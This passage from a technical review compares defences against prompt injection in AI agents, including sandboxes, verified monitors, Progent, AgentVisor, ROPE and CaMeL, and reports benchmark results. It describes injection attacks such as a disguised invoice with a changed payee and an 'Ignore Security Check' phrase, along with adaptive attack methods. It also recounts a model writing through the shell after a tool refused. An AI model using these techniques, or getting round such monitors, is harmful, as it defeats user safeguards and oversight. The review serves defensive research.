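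| Stopping tasks and restricting helper agents | One agent reported a task as stopped while it was still running, and helpers always had their parent's permissions |
| Limiting memory and hiding secrets | No agent offered a memory limit, and one process could read keys held by another |

The first result matters most for containment. One agent's file tool refuses to write outside the project folder. When a real model used that agent, it wrote the file through the shell in all five runs, in four of them after the tool had refused. No attacker was involved, and the model was trying to finish its task.

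Where a protection was missing, the model's own behavior often compensated, for example when it reread a file before changing it. This helps against accidents, but an operator cannot rely on it against prompt injection, because the attacker's text influences that same behavior.

Of the 25 tested verdicts, 16 matched the researchers' earlier analysis, seven became more precise, and two changed from missing to degraded. Most of the other verdicts rest on analysis alone. The experiments covered one model and particular versions of three products, and ran without a person at the keyboard. The researchers also point out that five identical results out of five are compatible with a true rate as low as 57%. The study did not measure how often attacks succeed.

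### Reading a request differently from the system

A monitor approves or blocks a request based on how it interprets it, but another program carries the request out. If the two interpret the request differently, the monitor may approve one action while the system performs another.

Suppose Alice's agent runs the shell command `cp "$FILE" summaries/`. The command's text does not show which file it will copy, because the shell fills in the value of `FILE` only when it runs the command. The text of a command that starts a Python script shows even less. For this reason, Sistla and colleagues designed Tether to evaluate a command by its system calls.

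A smaller version of the same problem remains, because Tether's guarantees hold only if it correctly translates system calls into actions such as "copy" or "upload". Sistla and colleagues tested this translation by fuzzing, which means running a program on large numbers of generated inputs, but their proofs assume that the translation is correct.

A request can also change after the monitor checks it. System-call wrappers, an older kind of monitor, checked the values a program passed to the kernel, but another part of the program could change those values before the kernel used them. *Ring-0 by Default* warns that hooks on an agent's tool calls have the same weakness.

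*Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) proves that an agent never enters a forbidden state, assuming that each action does exactly what the monitor checked and has no other effects. The agent starts in a safe state, and each approved action leads from one safe state to another, so by induction every state it reaches is safe. Because of that assumption, the proof doesn't cover a shell command with an effect that the monitor's model leaves out.

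The operator can avoid much of the trouble by giving the agent only tools whose requests have a single meaning. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) describes a monitor that also stores the texts and addresses used in requests. The agent receives only a name for each one and puts that name in its requests. The monitor looks up the value, checks it and passes the same value to the tool, so the agent cannot have one text checked and send another.

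### Settings and records within the agent's reach

An agent that runs under its user's account can usually write to the same files as its user, and these may include the monitor's settings. *Ring-0 by Default* showed that all three agents it studied could change their monitors' settings files, but it did not test whether the changes took effect.

Other files can matter as much as the settings. In one of the three products, the model that reviews actions stores its verdict in a file that the agent can write to. If an agent accepts a forged entry in its session records as a message from Alice, a monitor that trusts Alice's messages will trust that entry too, and a fence that reacts only to untrusted content will not activate. Tether's secrecy labels would also need protection, because a file with an altered label could leave the machine as public data.

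Running the monitor in a separate process from the agent protects the monitor's memory, but not its files if both processes use the same account. To protect the files as well, the operator can run the monitor under a different account or outside the virtual machine. Agenra's prototype offers less separation because it runs the agent and monitor in a single Python process, and Shivakumar and colleagues state that the boundary between them does not isolate arbitrary Python code. The prototype therefore suits an agent that can only call the tools it has been given, but would not contain one that runs its own code in that process.

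Users also like to change permissions mid-task, and the easiest way is to ask the agent. But if the agent can change a permission because Alice asked, it can also change it because of an instruction written in the invoice.

### A correct monitor with the wrong policy

A monitor can follow its rules exactly and still permit the wrong thing, because somebody has to state in advance what each task needs.

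Shivakumar and colleagues show how many rules even a simple task requires. Their agent is allowed to send the public parts of a private report to one person, once. If the only rule were that the text must be public, the agent could send that person unrelated public text. They therefore add a rule that the text must come from the tool that removes the private parts. But an injection could make the agent run that tool on the attacker's text and use up its only permission on the wrong document, so a further rule has to specify what goes into the tool. Agenra can enforce each of these rules, but it cannot alert the developer to a missing one.

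Changes to a policy can also have surprising effects. Suppose Alice's policy lists a permission for one payment to Bob's firm, then a permission for one payment to Carol's, and the monitor always uses the first permission that fits. Alice then extends the first permission to cover either firm. If the agent pays Carol's firm first, it uses up the extended permission. The remaining permission covers only Carol's firm, so the agent can pay her firm again but can't pay Bob's, though Alice wanted one payment to each.

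Agenra can check a change for the first of these problems. It approves a change only if it can establish that every sequence of calls that worked under the old policy still works under the new one. Shivakumar and colleagues wrote 51 test changes, of which 21 met this condition. Agenra approved all 21 and none of the others. The check does not test whether a change is safe. For example, raising the limit from one email to two preserves every earlier sequence, but it also lets the agent send the report twice.

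A policy can also be too narrow. In *Team BlueMoon*, Munson, Asch and colleagues had one model predict from the user's request which tools an agent would need and in what order. A monitor stopped the agent as soon as it did anything else. In one example with a small model, the user wanted to post a question in the channel with the most members. The agent correctly listed the channels and tried to post, but the monitor stopped it because the prediction included reading messages first.

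With GPT-4o, the prediction was right for 103 of 109 requests, but the prediction and the agent were both right for only 95. Most failures occurred because the two put the steps in different orders, even where either order could have worked. The predicting model also did poorly on requests such as "read all of my emails", because it had no way to determine how many emails there were.

### Progent: a model drafts the rules

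Alice will not write a new policy for every request, so *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) has a language model draft it. At first, this model reads only her request and the tool descriptions. For "summarise the March invoice", it might permit the agent to read that one file and nothing else. An ordinary program then checks every tool call against the rules and blocks any call that no rule permits.

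Some tasks need more permissions partway through. In Shi and colleagues' example, a user asks the agent to do what a colleague's email says, and the email asks it to post a summary of recent messages on Slack. The agent now needs permission to read those messages and to post. After a tool call, the drafting model decides, without seeing the result, whether the policy may need an update. If so, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy. An injection in the result can influence this proposal.

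Progent therefore checks the proposal with a solver, a program that can determine whether a logical formula holds in every case. If *A*(*P*) is the set of tool calls that a policy *P* permits, a new policy *P*′ takes effect automatically only if

*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*)

A policy update needs no approval if the new policy permits nothing the old one did not. Any other update needs approval from a person or from a rule the user has set. An injection can make the model request permission to email the attacker, but it cannot grant that permission. In Shi and colleagues' tests on AgentDojo, only 6% of updates needed approval.

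*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that a malicious tool result could lead Progent to relax its own policy. The objection seems to concern an earlier version without the solver. It still applies if the approver accepts every policy expansion, as in Shi and colleagues' main tests, which simulate a careless user. In those tests, the share of successful attacks on AgentDojo still fell from 39.9% to 1.0%. Because no expansion was refused, the improvement came from the quality of the drafted rules rather than from the solver.

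The solver's check only compares each policy with the previous one, so it cannot detect that the first policy was too broad. It also treats every narrower policy as safe. Suppose Alice's policy permits payments to any account, and the hidden line in her invoice causes the model to restrict payments to the attacker's account. The new policy permits fewer calls, so Progent applies it without asking for approval, and the agent can then pay only the attacker.

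The argument for having a model write the policy is that the practical alternative is often one broad policy for all tasks. A policy drafted only from Alice's request can exclude most tools before the agent reads anything. Progent also lets the operator write a fixed policy that takes priority over the draft. If the fixed policy forbids payments to new accounts, no draft can permit them.

### What else has to work

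The part that decides on requests is often the smallest part of the trusted computing base. Both Tether and Agenra make their decisions in Lean, which is a programming language as well as a proof assistant, and both depend on much more:

| Monitor | What its developers also trust |
|---|---|
| Tether | The host's kernel, the software that records system calls, the temporary file layer, the network proxy, the translation into actions, and Lean itself |
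| Agenra | The Python code that translates the policy and passes on calls, the tools, the scanners, the labels given to data sources, and Lean's compiler and runtime |

Tether's guarantees don't cover attacks on the kernel or escapes from the sandbox. If the monitor runs outside the agent's virtual machine, it depends on the hypervisor instead of the guest's kernel, so its guarantees can be no stronger than the hypervisor.

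Tool servers, the programs that supply an agent with tools, are harder to assess because other people often write and run them. When the monitor approves a call, it relies on the server to run the tool as described. In Agenra's example, the agent may send the report only to an address from the company directory. If an attacker has changed the directory, the report goes to the attacker even though the monitor enforces its rule correctly.

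A tool's description can also carry an injection, and *Ring-0 by Default* points out that a server can change it after the user installs the tool. The study found that agents install tool servers and other extensions without signatures, fixed versions or a binding list of permissions. It recommends checking signatures and versions each time the agent loads an extension, since a check at installation misses later changes.

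Updates to the agent, the kernel or the monitor also make the monitor harder to trust. A test or proof applies to one version, and the next may add a tool or a route that nobody has examined. Never updating would leave known flaws unfixed, so someone has to repeat the checks after each update, which is easier if they run automatically.

### AgentVisor: a model checks the meaning

Fixed rules compare names, paths, amounts and labels. If Alice allows her agent to email the supplier, a rule can check the address but cannot distinguish a question about the invoice from a promise to pay double. Making that distinction requires some understanding of what Alice asked the agent to do.

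Ying, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *AgentVisor*, give this task to a second language model, which answers three questions about each tool call:

- Does the tool suit the assistant's role?
- Does the call serve the user's request or a reasonable step towards it?
- Do the details, such as the recipient, match what the user specified?

Models can often recognise an injection when asked about it, yet follow it while working on a task, so the checking model does not work on the task. It reads the developer's instructions, the user's request, a cleaned record of earlier steps and the proposed call, but never the documents. If it rejects a call, it explains why, and the agent gets one chance to correct it. In tests by Ying and colleagues, agents under attack through documents completed 67% of their tasks when they had this second chance, compared with 13% when the checker simply blocked bad calls.

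Hiding the documents reduces the attacker's influence on the checker but does not remove it. The proposed call may contain text that the agent copied from the invoice, and that text could be addressed to the checker. The record of earlier steps also includes short summaries of what the tools returned. In AgentVisor's published procedure, the corrected call runs without another check, so nothing in AgentVisor stops the second attempt if the agent is still following the attacker's instruction.

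Ying and colleagues report that attack success fell to 0.65%. They also attacked the checker with phrases such as "Ignore Security Check", and none of these attacks succeeded. This is a weak test because a determined attacker would try many wordings and keep the ones that work.

*Ring-0 by Default* tested the checking models in two deployed products. When the researchers simulated broken, missing or late replies from these models, both products blocked the action, which is the safe way to fail. The models also approved 30 of 30 harmless actions in one product and 14 of 15 in the other. But both models received the text of the action, and one also received the agent's justification for it. The researchers chose not to search for text that would make a model approve something harmful, so the results do not show how hard that is.

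A checking model is safest when it runs after a set of fixed rules and can only add to what they block. If an attacker deceives the model, the agent can still do only what the rules allow. The reviewer in Kairos has a similar limit, since it can release only effects that the policy has deferred to it.

### What developers can verify now

seL4 is a small operating system kernel with a mathematical proof that its code meets its specification. *Ring-0 by Default* cites it as evidence that a real kernel can satisfy Anderson's third requirement.

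A kernel of this kind has a narrow job. It divides up memory and processor time, passes messages between programs, and checks whether a program has the right to what it requests. Its developers can define each of these operations exactly, and none of them depends on why a program requests a file. A monitor that enforces only a list of permitted paths and connections has a job just as narrow. Its specification grows once it must also determine what a shell command does, where a value came from, or which supplier Alice meant.

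Researchers can already prove some properties of how a monitor makes decisions. Sistla and colleagues prove in Lean that the order of Tether's rules does not affect the outcome and that a refused request leaves the monitor's security state unchanged. The prototype runs the same Lean definitions that the proofs describe, without translation into another language. A faster version in another language would need extensive tests to confirm that it always agrees with the Lean version. Agenra's proofs also cover the code that makes its decisions, but they assume that the agent makes one call at a time, and many agents make several at once.

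Developers can also prove that a policy has a stated property. With Tether, they can prove that a policy never permits network access after the agent has read a sensitive file. This catches mistakes in a long list of rules, but someone still has to think of the property to prove.

*PerMIT* (2026) applies the same method to an agent's long-term memory. Its proofs treat the protected model as an arbitrary function of what it can see, so they hold no matter how the model behaves. They also assume that the attacker controls every tool result and everything the quarantined model returns. The proofs cover only a single-user interface and leave out some repeated operations.

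| Part of the system | What a proof can cover now | What stays open |
|---|---|---|
| Decision on a request | That the code applies the rules correctly | Whether the monitor's description of the request matches what will happen |
| Policy | That it has a stated property, or permits no more than an earlier version | Whether it fits the user's task |
| Memory and labels | That untrusted data cannot become trusted except by defined steps | Whether the first labels are right |
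| Kernel or hypervisor | That a small one meets its specification | Hardware faults and mistakes in the configuration |
| Tools and tool servers | That a simple tool does only what it declares | Services that other companies run and change |
| Model used as a checker | That it cannot overrule the fixed rules | Whether its judgements are right |

Alice's invoice agent could come close to Anderson's standard. It reads one folder, writes to another and needs no shell, so each request has one meaning. Its four-line policy is short enough to check by reading. Developers could verify a monitor for these two tools with existing methods, though most would still run it on an unverified kernel. A programming agent that runs arbitrary commands needs something like Tether's translation of system calls, which its developers have tested but not proved correct.

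## Comparison with other defences against prompt injection

Most defences other than containment try to stop the model from obeying the hidden line in Alice's invoice, or to detect the attack in time. In their survey, Wang and colleagues sort defences by whether they act on the text the model reads, the model itself, or the tool calls it writes.

### How the alternatives work

Spotlighting marks untrusted text so that the model can tell it apart from the user's instructions. In the version that Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) tested in *AutoDojo*, the agent's program puts markers around everything a tool returns, and the developer tells the model in the system prompt never to follow instructions between them. Other developers put a reminder before the text or repeat the user's request after it. These methods take little compute and work with any model, but the injected instruction stays in the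 context and the model can still obey it.

Developers can also train the model to prefer the user's instructions. With the instruction hierarchy, they rank messages by source and train the model to follow the higher-ranked one when two conflict. StruQ and SecAlign similarly train a model to ignore instructions in the part of its input reserved for data. Such training makes the model less likely to obey injected instructions, but it may still obey them. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites tests of the instruction hierarchy on GPT-4o-mini in which existing attacks, not adapted to the defence, still scored 0.68 and 0.75 on a scale from 0 to 1.

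A classifier, such as PromptGuard, PIGuard or a detector from the company ProtectAI, is usually a small model that scores text for signs of an injection. In the AutoDojo tests, these classifiers scored each sentence a tool returned, and the program deleted the suspicious ones before the agent read the rest. DataFilter is a language model that reads the text together with the user's request and returns a copy with suspected injections removed. Any of these defences can miss an injection or delete a sentence the agent needs.

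Other defences check whether each action fits the task. AgentVisor does this with a second language model. In DRIFT, a model predicts the sequence of tool calls from the user's request, and a model later evaluates any departure from that sequence. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request masked. If the agent makes the same tool call again, the document probably caused it. Claude Code's auto mode uses a classifier that approves or blocks commands in place of the user. According to Anthropic, the classifier stops about 83% of actions that go beyond what the user wanted and wrongly blocks about 0.4% of harmless commands.

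### Why a low success rate is not a guarantee

An attack success rate records how often particular attacks worked against a particular model. A guarantee covers every attack of a stated kind, as long as its assumptions hold. The difference matters because attackers can try again. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of *n* attempts succeeds is

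1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

With *p* = 0.1% and *n* = 100, this gives 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰, or about 9.5%.

Anthropic reports that on a benchmark from Gray Swan, a company that tests the security of AI models, roughly 0.1% of single attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7. When attackers could make 100 adaptive attempts, they succeeded 5 to 6% of the time. A rate of exactly 0.1% would lead to 9.5% after 100 independent attempts. Rounding alone could explain the difference, because a true rate of 0.057% would round to 0.1% and lead to 5.5%.

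Attempts are not independent, though. Narisetty and colleagues quote results from Gray Swan's adaptive tests of an older model, Claude Opus 4.5. Attacks succeeded in 4.7% of cases after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63.0% after a hundred. If the attempts had been independent, the rates would have been 38% after ten and 99% after a hundred. Apparently, some targets are compromised early while others resist nearly every attempt.

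The attack success rate also depends on what the agent is doing. VentureBeat reports figures from the system card Anthropic published with Claude Opus 4.6. In a restricted programming environment, none of 200 attempts succeeded. When the model operated a graphical interface with extended thinking, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. By the 200th attempt, the figure had reached 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

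An attacker who sends Alice a hundred invoices may make her suspicious. But if he sends one invoice to each of 10,000 people whose agents fail 0.1% of the time, about ten of the attacks should succeed, and no recipient sees anything unusual.

A guarantee, by contrast, can fail completely when an assumption is false. For example, Cowork's list of permitted addresses gave no protection against an upload to the attacker's own account at one of them.

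### *The Attacker Moves Second*

Developers have mostly tested their defences against fixed attacks that existed before the defence did. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (October 2025), Nasr and colleagues instead designed attacks specifically for each of twelve published defences, most with reported attack success near zero.

The researchers attacked the defences in four ways. Where they had access to a model's weights, they calculated which changes to the injected text would make the model more likely to obey it. They also trained an attacking model by rewarding it for successful injections, and had a language model rewrite injections over many rounds. Finally, people attacked the defences by hand.

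According to Narisetty and colleagues, attack success rates rose above 90% against most of the twelve defences. They passed 95% against spotlighting and against repeating the user's request, and reached 96% against MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injections. The human attackers reached 100%.

These attackers knew the defence in full and had far more resources than most criminals would use against Alice, so Ma and colleagues read the study as evidence of what an attacker can break in principle. They also point out that it covers only prompting, training and filtering. It includes no defence that limits an agent's actions from outside the model, so it does not show whether monitors would have done better.

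### AgentDojo and its limits

Many published scores for containment and its alternatives come from AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates banking, messaging, travel and office applications. Each test case combines a user's task with an attacker's goal in the same application. Banking, for example, has 16 tasks and nine goals, which make 144 of the benchmark's 629 test cases.

The benchmark plants the attacker's text in something the agent will read, such as a file or a message. The agent then works on the task with simulated tools. Afterwards, a program checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal. Researchers usually report how often attacks succeed and the share of tasks the agent completes with and without an attack.

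The most common attack is a block of text presented as an important message from the user, telling the assistant to do another task first. A defence can score well by recognising this style. Wang and colleagues found that 14 of 37 attack papers use automated optimisation to generate injections, while developers still test defences mainly against hand-written ones. Newer models also tend to ignore the standard message. In the AutoDojo tests, the message succeeded in only 0.3% of cases against Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defence, so almost any defence added to that model would have appeared highly effective.

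The choice of tasks also favours some defences. In most benchmarks, the user's request specifies the task in full, so a defence that shuts out all outside content loses little usefulness. Wang and colleagues built AgentPI, a benchmark with five kinds of tasks in which the agent has to decide what to do based on what it reads. None of the eight defences they tested combined high security, high usefulness and low delay. Some defences that restrict actions cost up to three times as much as an undefended agent, and others refused so early that the agent could not do complex work.

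In a trial by Ma and colleagues, agents completed neither the user's task nor the attacker's goal in 52.9% of the office application's cases. These cases lower the average attack success even though they provide no evidence about a defence.

### AutoDojo: rewriting the attack

AutoDojo uses AgentDojo's applications but replaces the fixed message with one that adapts. It starts from existing attacks and ranks them by how often they work against the defended agent. A language model, Gemini 3.1 Pro, reads the ranking, suggests why some attempts worked and others failed, and writes a new injection. AutoDojo tests it, adds it to the ranking and repeats this six times. It shows the attacking model only how often each injection succeeded across the user tasks in which the agent reads the same document, and does not reveal the defence or the agent's reasoning.

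Ma and colleagues left out the office application, which leaves 389 cases. The table gives their results for agents that used GPT-4o-mini, now an old model:

| Defence | What it does | Tasks completed, no attack | Success of standard attack | Success of AutoDojo |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 66.7% | 58.6% | 52.4% |
| Reminder | Marks text | 68.4% | 39.3% | 40.4% |
| Spotlighting | Marks text | 59.6% | 51.7% | 46.8% |
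| PromptGuard | Filters text | 63.2% | 54.2% | 49.4% |
| PIGuard | Filters text | 43.9% | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| ProtectAI | Filters text | 47.4% | 7.2% | 15.4% |
| DataFilter | Filters text | 64.9% | 12.6% | 33.4% |
| DRIFT | Restricts actions | 49.1% | 2.6% | 6.4% |
| Progent | Restricts actions | 63.2% | 8.2% | 7.7% |
| ROPE | Restricts actions | 59.6% | 6.4% | 4.4% |
| CaMeL | Restricts actions | 26.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

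Against weak defences, AutoDojo sometimes did worse than the standard attack because Ma and colleagues did not let it return any of the attacks it started from. A real attacker would use whichever of the two worked better.

An attacker can get past PIGuard by adapting the injection. In one case, the user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. PIGuard deleted nearly all of the standard injection, so the agent had nothing to act on. AutoDojo wrote an ordinary-looking bill for 0.01, with the attacker's account as the payee and a notice that the payment details had changed. No sentence in it looked like a command to an AI, so PIGuard let it through and the agent paid. A better classifier might not have helped, because an honest supplier who changes banks would write much the same thing. Dongol's test does not count a changed payee as a breach.

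Attacks succeeded most often when the user left the most to the document. With PIGuard in place, AutoDojo succeeded in 17.3% of cases when the user specified the action and all its details, 31.1% when the agent had to look up a detail such as the payee, and 54.2% when the user made a request like "do everything on this list". The last figure comes from only four user tasks.

Defences that restrict actions resisted injections better, as Kairos did when its own developers tested it with AutoDojo. But Ma and colleagues ran each test only once, so small differences could be due to chance. They also searched for injections against DRIFT and Progent using a cheaper model inside those defences than in the final test, so an attacker who practised on the real configuration might succeed more often. Four of AutoDojo's six developers also developed ROPE.

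### An adaptive attack on Progent

In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent alone. They work for LaunchSafe, which builds its own agent security tools on the same principle, and their study has not been peer reviewed.

The researchers attacked the only part of Progent that contains a language model, the part that drafts and updates the policy. Their injection described the attacker's action as a necessary step that was already authorised, in the hope that this model would permit it. A small open model, Qwen2.5-7B, acted as the agent and wrote the policies. The researchers combined eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo applications with every attacker's goal, and ran the test three times.

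| Application | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adapted attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Messaging | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent withstood the adapted attack, but these percentages are based on few successful attacks. Over all three runs, successful attacks rose from four to eight out of 216 in banking and fell from 13 to five out of 120 in messaging. The office tasks don't test the defence, because the model ignored those injections even without it.

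Narisetty and colleagues think the disguise may have backfired, because an injection that looks routine may influence the policy model more easily but be less likely to make the agent act. The low figure could therefore reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. They did not try gradient-based attacks or an attack that uses only tools the policy already permits, and one would expect a monitor to be weak against the latter.

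The defence reduced the share of tasks the agent completed under the standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the defended agent needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

### ROPE: checking where a value came from

*ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) presents a monitor that checks where the important values in a tool call came from. CaMeL also does this, but ROPE adjusts its rules to each request and lets the agent plan as it goes.

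Before anyone uses an agent protected by ROPE, its developer lists the values an attacker could use to do harm, such as the recipient of a payment, and gives each a default rule for which sources it may come from. When Alice makes a request, a language model reads the request and trusted account data, but no documents, and changes the rules where the task requires it. A rule can allow values from her request, from an authenticated sender she named, or from her own records. Whenever the agent tries to change or send something, an ordinary program checks that each listed value appears in full in an allowed source. ROPE does not accept values from a file whose text an attacker could have written, even if Alice named the file.

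Ma and colleagues prove that a value that appears only in text an attacker could write never reaches a tool through one of these guarded fields. They also prove that rewording untrusted text never changes ROPE's decision about a given value, though it may change what the agent tries to do. The proofs assume that the platform identifies senders correctly, that the user's records contain no values from an attacker, and that the developer's list is complete.

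On AgentDyn, the benchmark whose tasks change along the way, ROPE reduced the standard attack's success rate on GPT-4o-mini from 49.6% to 0.3%. The share of tasks completed when there was no attack also fell, from 46.7% to 36.7%. Agents completed only 6.7% of tasks with Progent and none with CaMeL, partly because CaMeL needs detailed policies for each application.

ROPE also refuses some legitimate payments. In one test, a user asks the agent to download an electricity bill and pay it. The company's account number appears only in the bill, so ROPE blocks the payment even without an attack. It would treat an invoice from one of Alice's new suppliers the same way.

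Across all the models and both benchmarks, 51 standard attacks got past ROPE, and Ma and colleagues examined each one:

- In 23 cases, the agent recommended the attacker's hotel in its reply to the user, which involves no tool call.
- In 21 cases, the harm was in the text of a message to a permitted recipient, such as a phishing link sent to a colleague the user had named.
- In seven cases, the user had left a sensitive value entirely to text that an attacker could write.

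None of these contradicts the proofs, which do not cover replies, free text or unguarded values.

The same study also found a fault in AgentDojo's scoring. For one of the attacker's goals in the messaging application, the benchmark counts the attack as successful once the agent requests the action, even if a monitor then refuses it. Ma and colleagues corrected this for every defence. In their study, the standard attack on GPT-4o-mini succeeded against ROPE in 3.7% of AgentDojo cases, compared with 6.4% in the AutoDojo table. The correction may explain part of the difference.

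### Six designs side by side

Scores from different studies can look comparable when they are not, so the next table marks where each figure comes from:

- **A:** AutoDojo's attacks on GPT-4o-mini. Without a defence, the agent completed 66.7% of tasks and 52.4% of attacks succeeded.
- **B:** The developers' own tests, with other models or attacks.
- **C:** Narisetty and colleagues' test with Qwen2.5-7B.

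Only figures with the same letter A are comparable with each other.

| Design | What it guarantees | What it assumes | Attack success | Tasks completed, no attack | Cost | In a widely used agent? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | Documents cannot add tool calls, and each call's data must satisfy the policy | Correct policies and interpreter; no side channels | 0.0% (A) | 26.3% (A) | About 2.8 times the tokens (B) | Unclear |
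| FIDES | Consequential calls depend only on trusted data, and data goes only to permitted readers | Correct labels and policies; no leaks through timing or the choice of calls | No comparable figure | No comparable figure | No comparable figure | Unclear |
| Progent | No call outside the current policy runs | The policy fits the task, and whoever approves changes is careful | 7.7% (A) | 63.2% (A) | About 15 times the model calls (C) | Unclear |
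| AgentVisor | Nothing | The checking model judges correctly | 0.65% (B) | 1.45% below an undefended agent (B) | A model check for each tool call | Unclear |
| ROPE | Guarded values come from accepted sources | Truthful sender data, clean records, a complete list of sensitive values | 4.4% (A) | 59.6% (A) | One model call per task, plus the list | Unclear |
| Plain sandbox | Programs inside reach only permitted files and addresses | A sound kernel or hypervisor and a correct configuration | No comparable figure | No comparable figure | Little delay for an operating-system sandbox; a virtual machine has to start up | Yes |

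AgentVisor's figure comes from tests that used mostly weak attacks. Ying and colleagues hid seven hand-written attacks in AgentDojo's documents. Against an agent with no defence, six of them succeeded in fewer than 4% of cases, which left AgentVisor little to prevent. The seventh, the standard message, succeeded in 45%. No attacker in these tests rewrote an injection after seeing it fail.

The share of tasks CaMeL completes depends heavily on the model that writes the plan. Its developers report that with OpenAI's o3 it completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. In the AutoDojo tests without an attack, which left out the office application, CaMeL completed 26.3% of tasks with GPT-4o-mini and 52.6% with the newer GPT-5.4-mini. CaMeL can still complete far fewer tasks than an undefended agent when both use a newer model. With Claude Haiku 4.5,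 it completed 40.4%, while the undefended agent completed 70.2%.

The plain sandbox is the only one of the six defences that has clearly been adopted, in Claude Code and Anthropic's other products. It doesn't need a policy for each task or a second model. When Anthropic introduced sandboxing in Claude Code, it claimed that "even a successful prompt injection is fully isolated". That claim was too strong, because an injection can still misuse any file or address the sandbox lets the agent reach, as the later theft through Cowork showed.

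It is harder to explain why the others have spread less. CaMeL requires developers to rebuild their agent, but Progent can run as a proxy in front of an existing one. Narisetty and colleagues mention a deployed version of FIDES that treats unlabelled data as trusted, but they do not name a product. Tasks that fail because of the defence may be a greater obstacle than installation, since users notice a refused payment at once but may never notice a prevented attack.

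### Combining a better model with containment

A well-trained model can reduce measured attack success more than most added defences do. In one AutoDojo test, only seven of 389 attacks succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5 with no added defence. Adding Progent reduced this to two, but the share of tasks completed when there was no attack also fell, from 70.2% to 63.2%. These figures may understate the benefit of containment, because AutoDojo had only six rounds to find an injection, and Gray Swan's results show how success rates grow when an attacker has a hundred.

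Once a monitor is in place, a better model mainly helps with harms that the monitor permits. For example, the model's tendency to ignore the hidden line is the only automatic protection against a false figure in Alice's summary. The same applies to the promoted hotel and the phishing link that got past ROPE. A model that rarely obeys injections also makes fewer forbidden requests, so the monitor interrupts Alice less often and she can give each question more attention.

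Containment protects against attacks that give the model no reason to refuse, such as the malicious prompt that an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into pasting. Anthropic therefore advises developers to limit the agent's environment before working on the model's behavior. It describes auto mode's classifier as a layer for use inside a sandbox, not a replacement for one.

The combined protection of a model and a monitor is hard to calculate. If a model obeys 1% of injections and a monitor misses 5% of the resulting actions, multiplying the two gives an attack success rate of 0.05%. This figure is valid only if the failures are independent, and an attacker will look for a single text that defeats both defences.

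Some evidence suggests that a text that defeats more than one layer is harder to write than one that defeats a single layer. In a variation of the AutoDojo test, Ma and colleagues told the attacking model why each injection had failed and how PIGuard had scored it. Attack success fell from 28.0% to 23.4%, because the model wrote text that passed the filter but no longer persuaded the agent. Narisetty and colleagues suspect the same effect in their attack on Progent. Both tests gave the attacker far fewer resources than *The Attacker Moves Second* did, and with more attempts an attacker may well find wording that defeats both layers.
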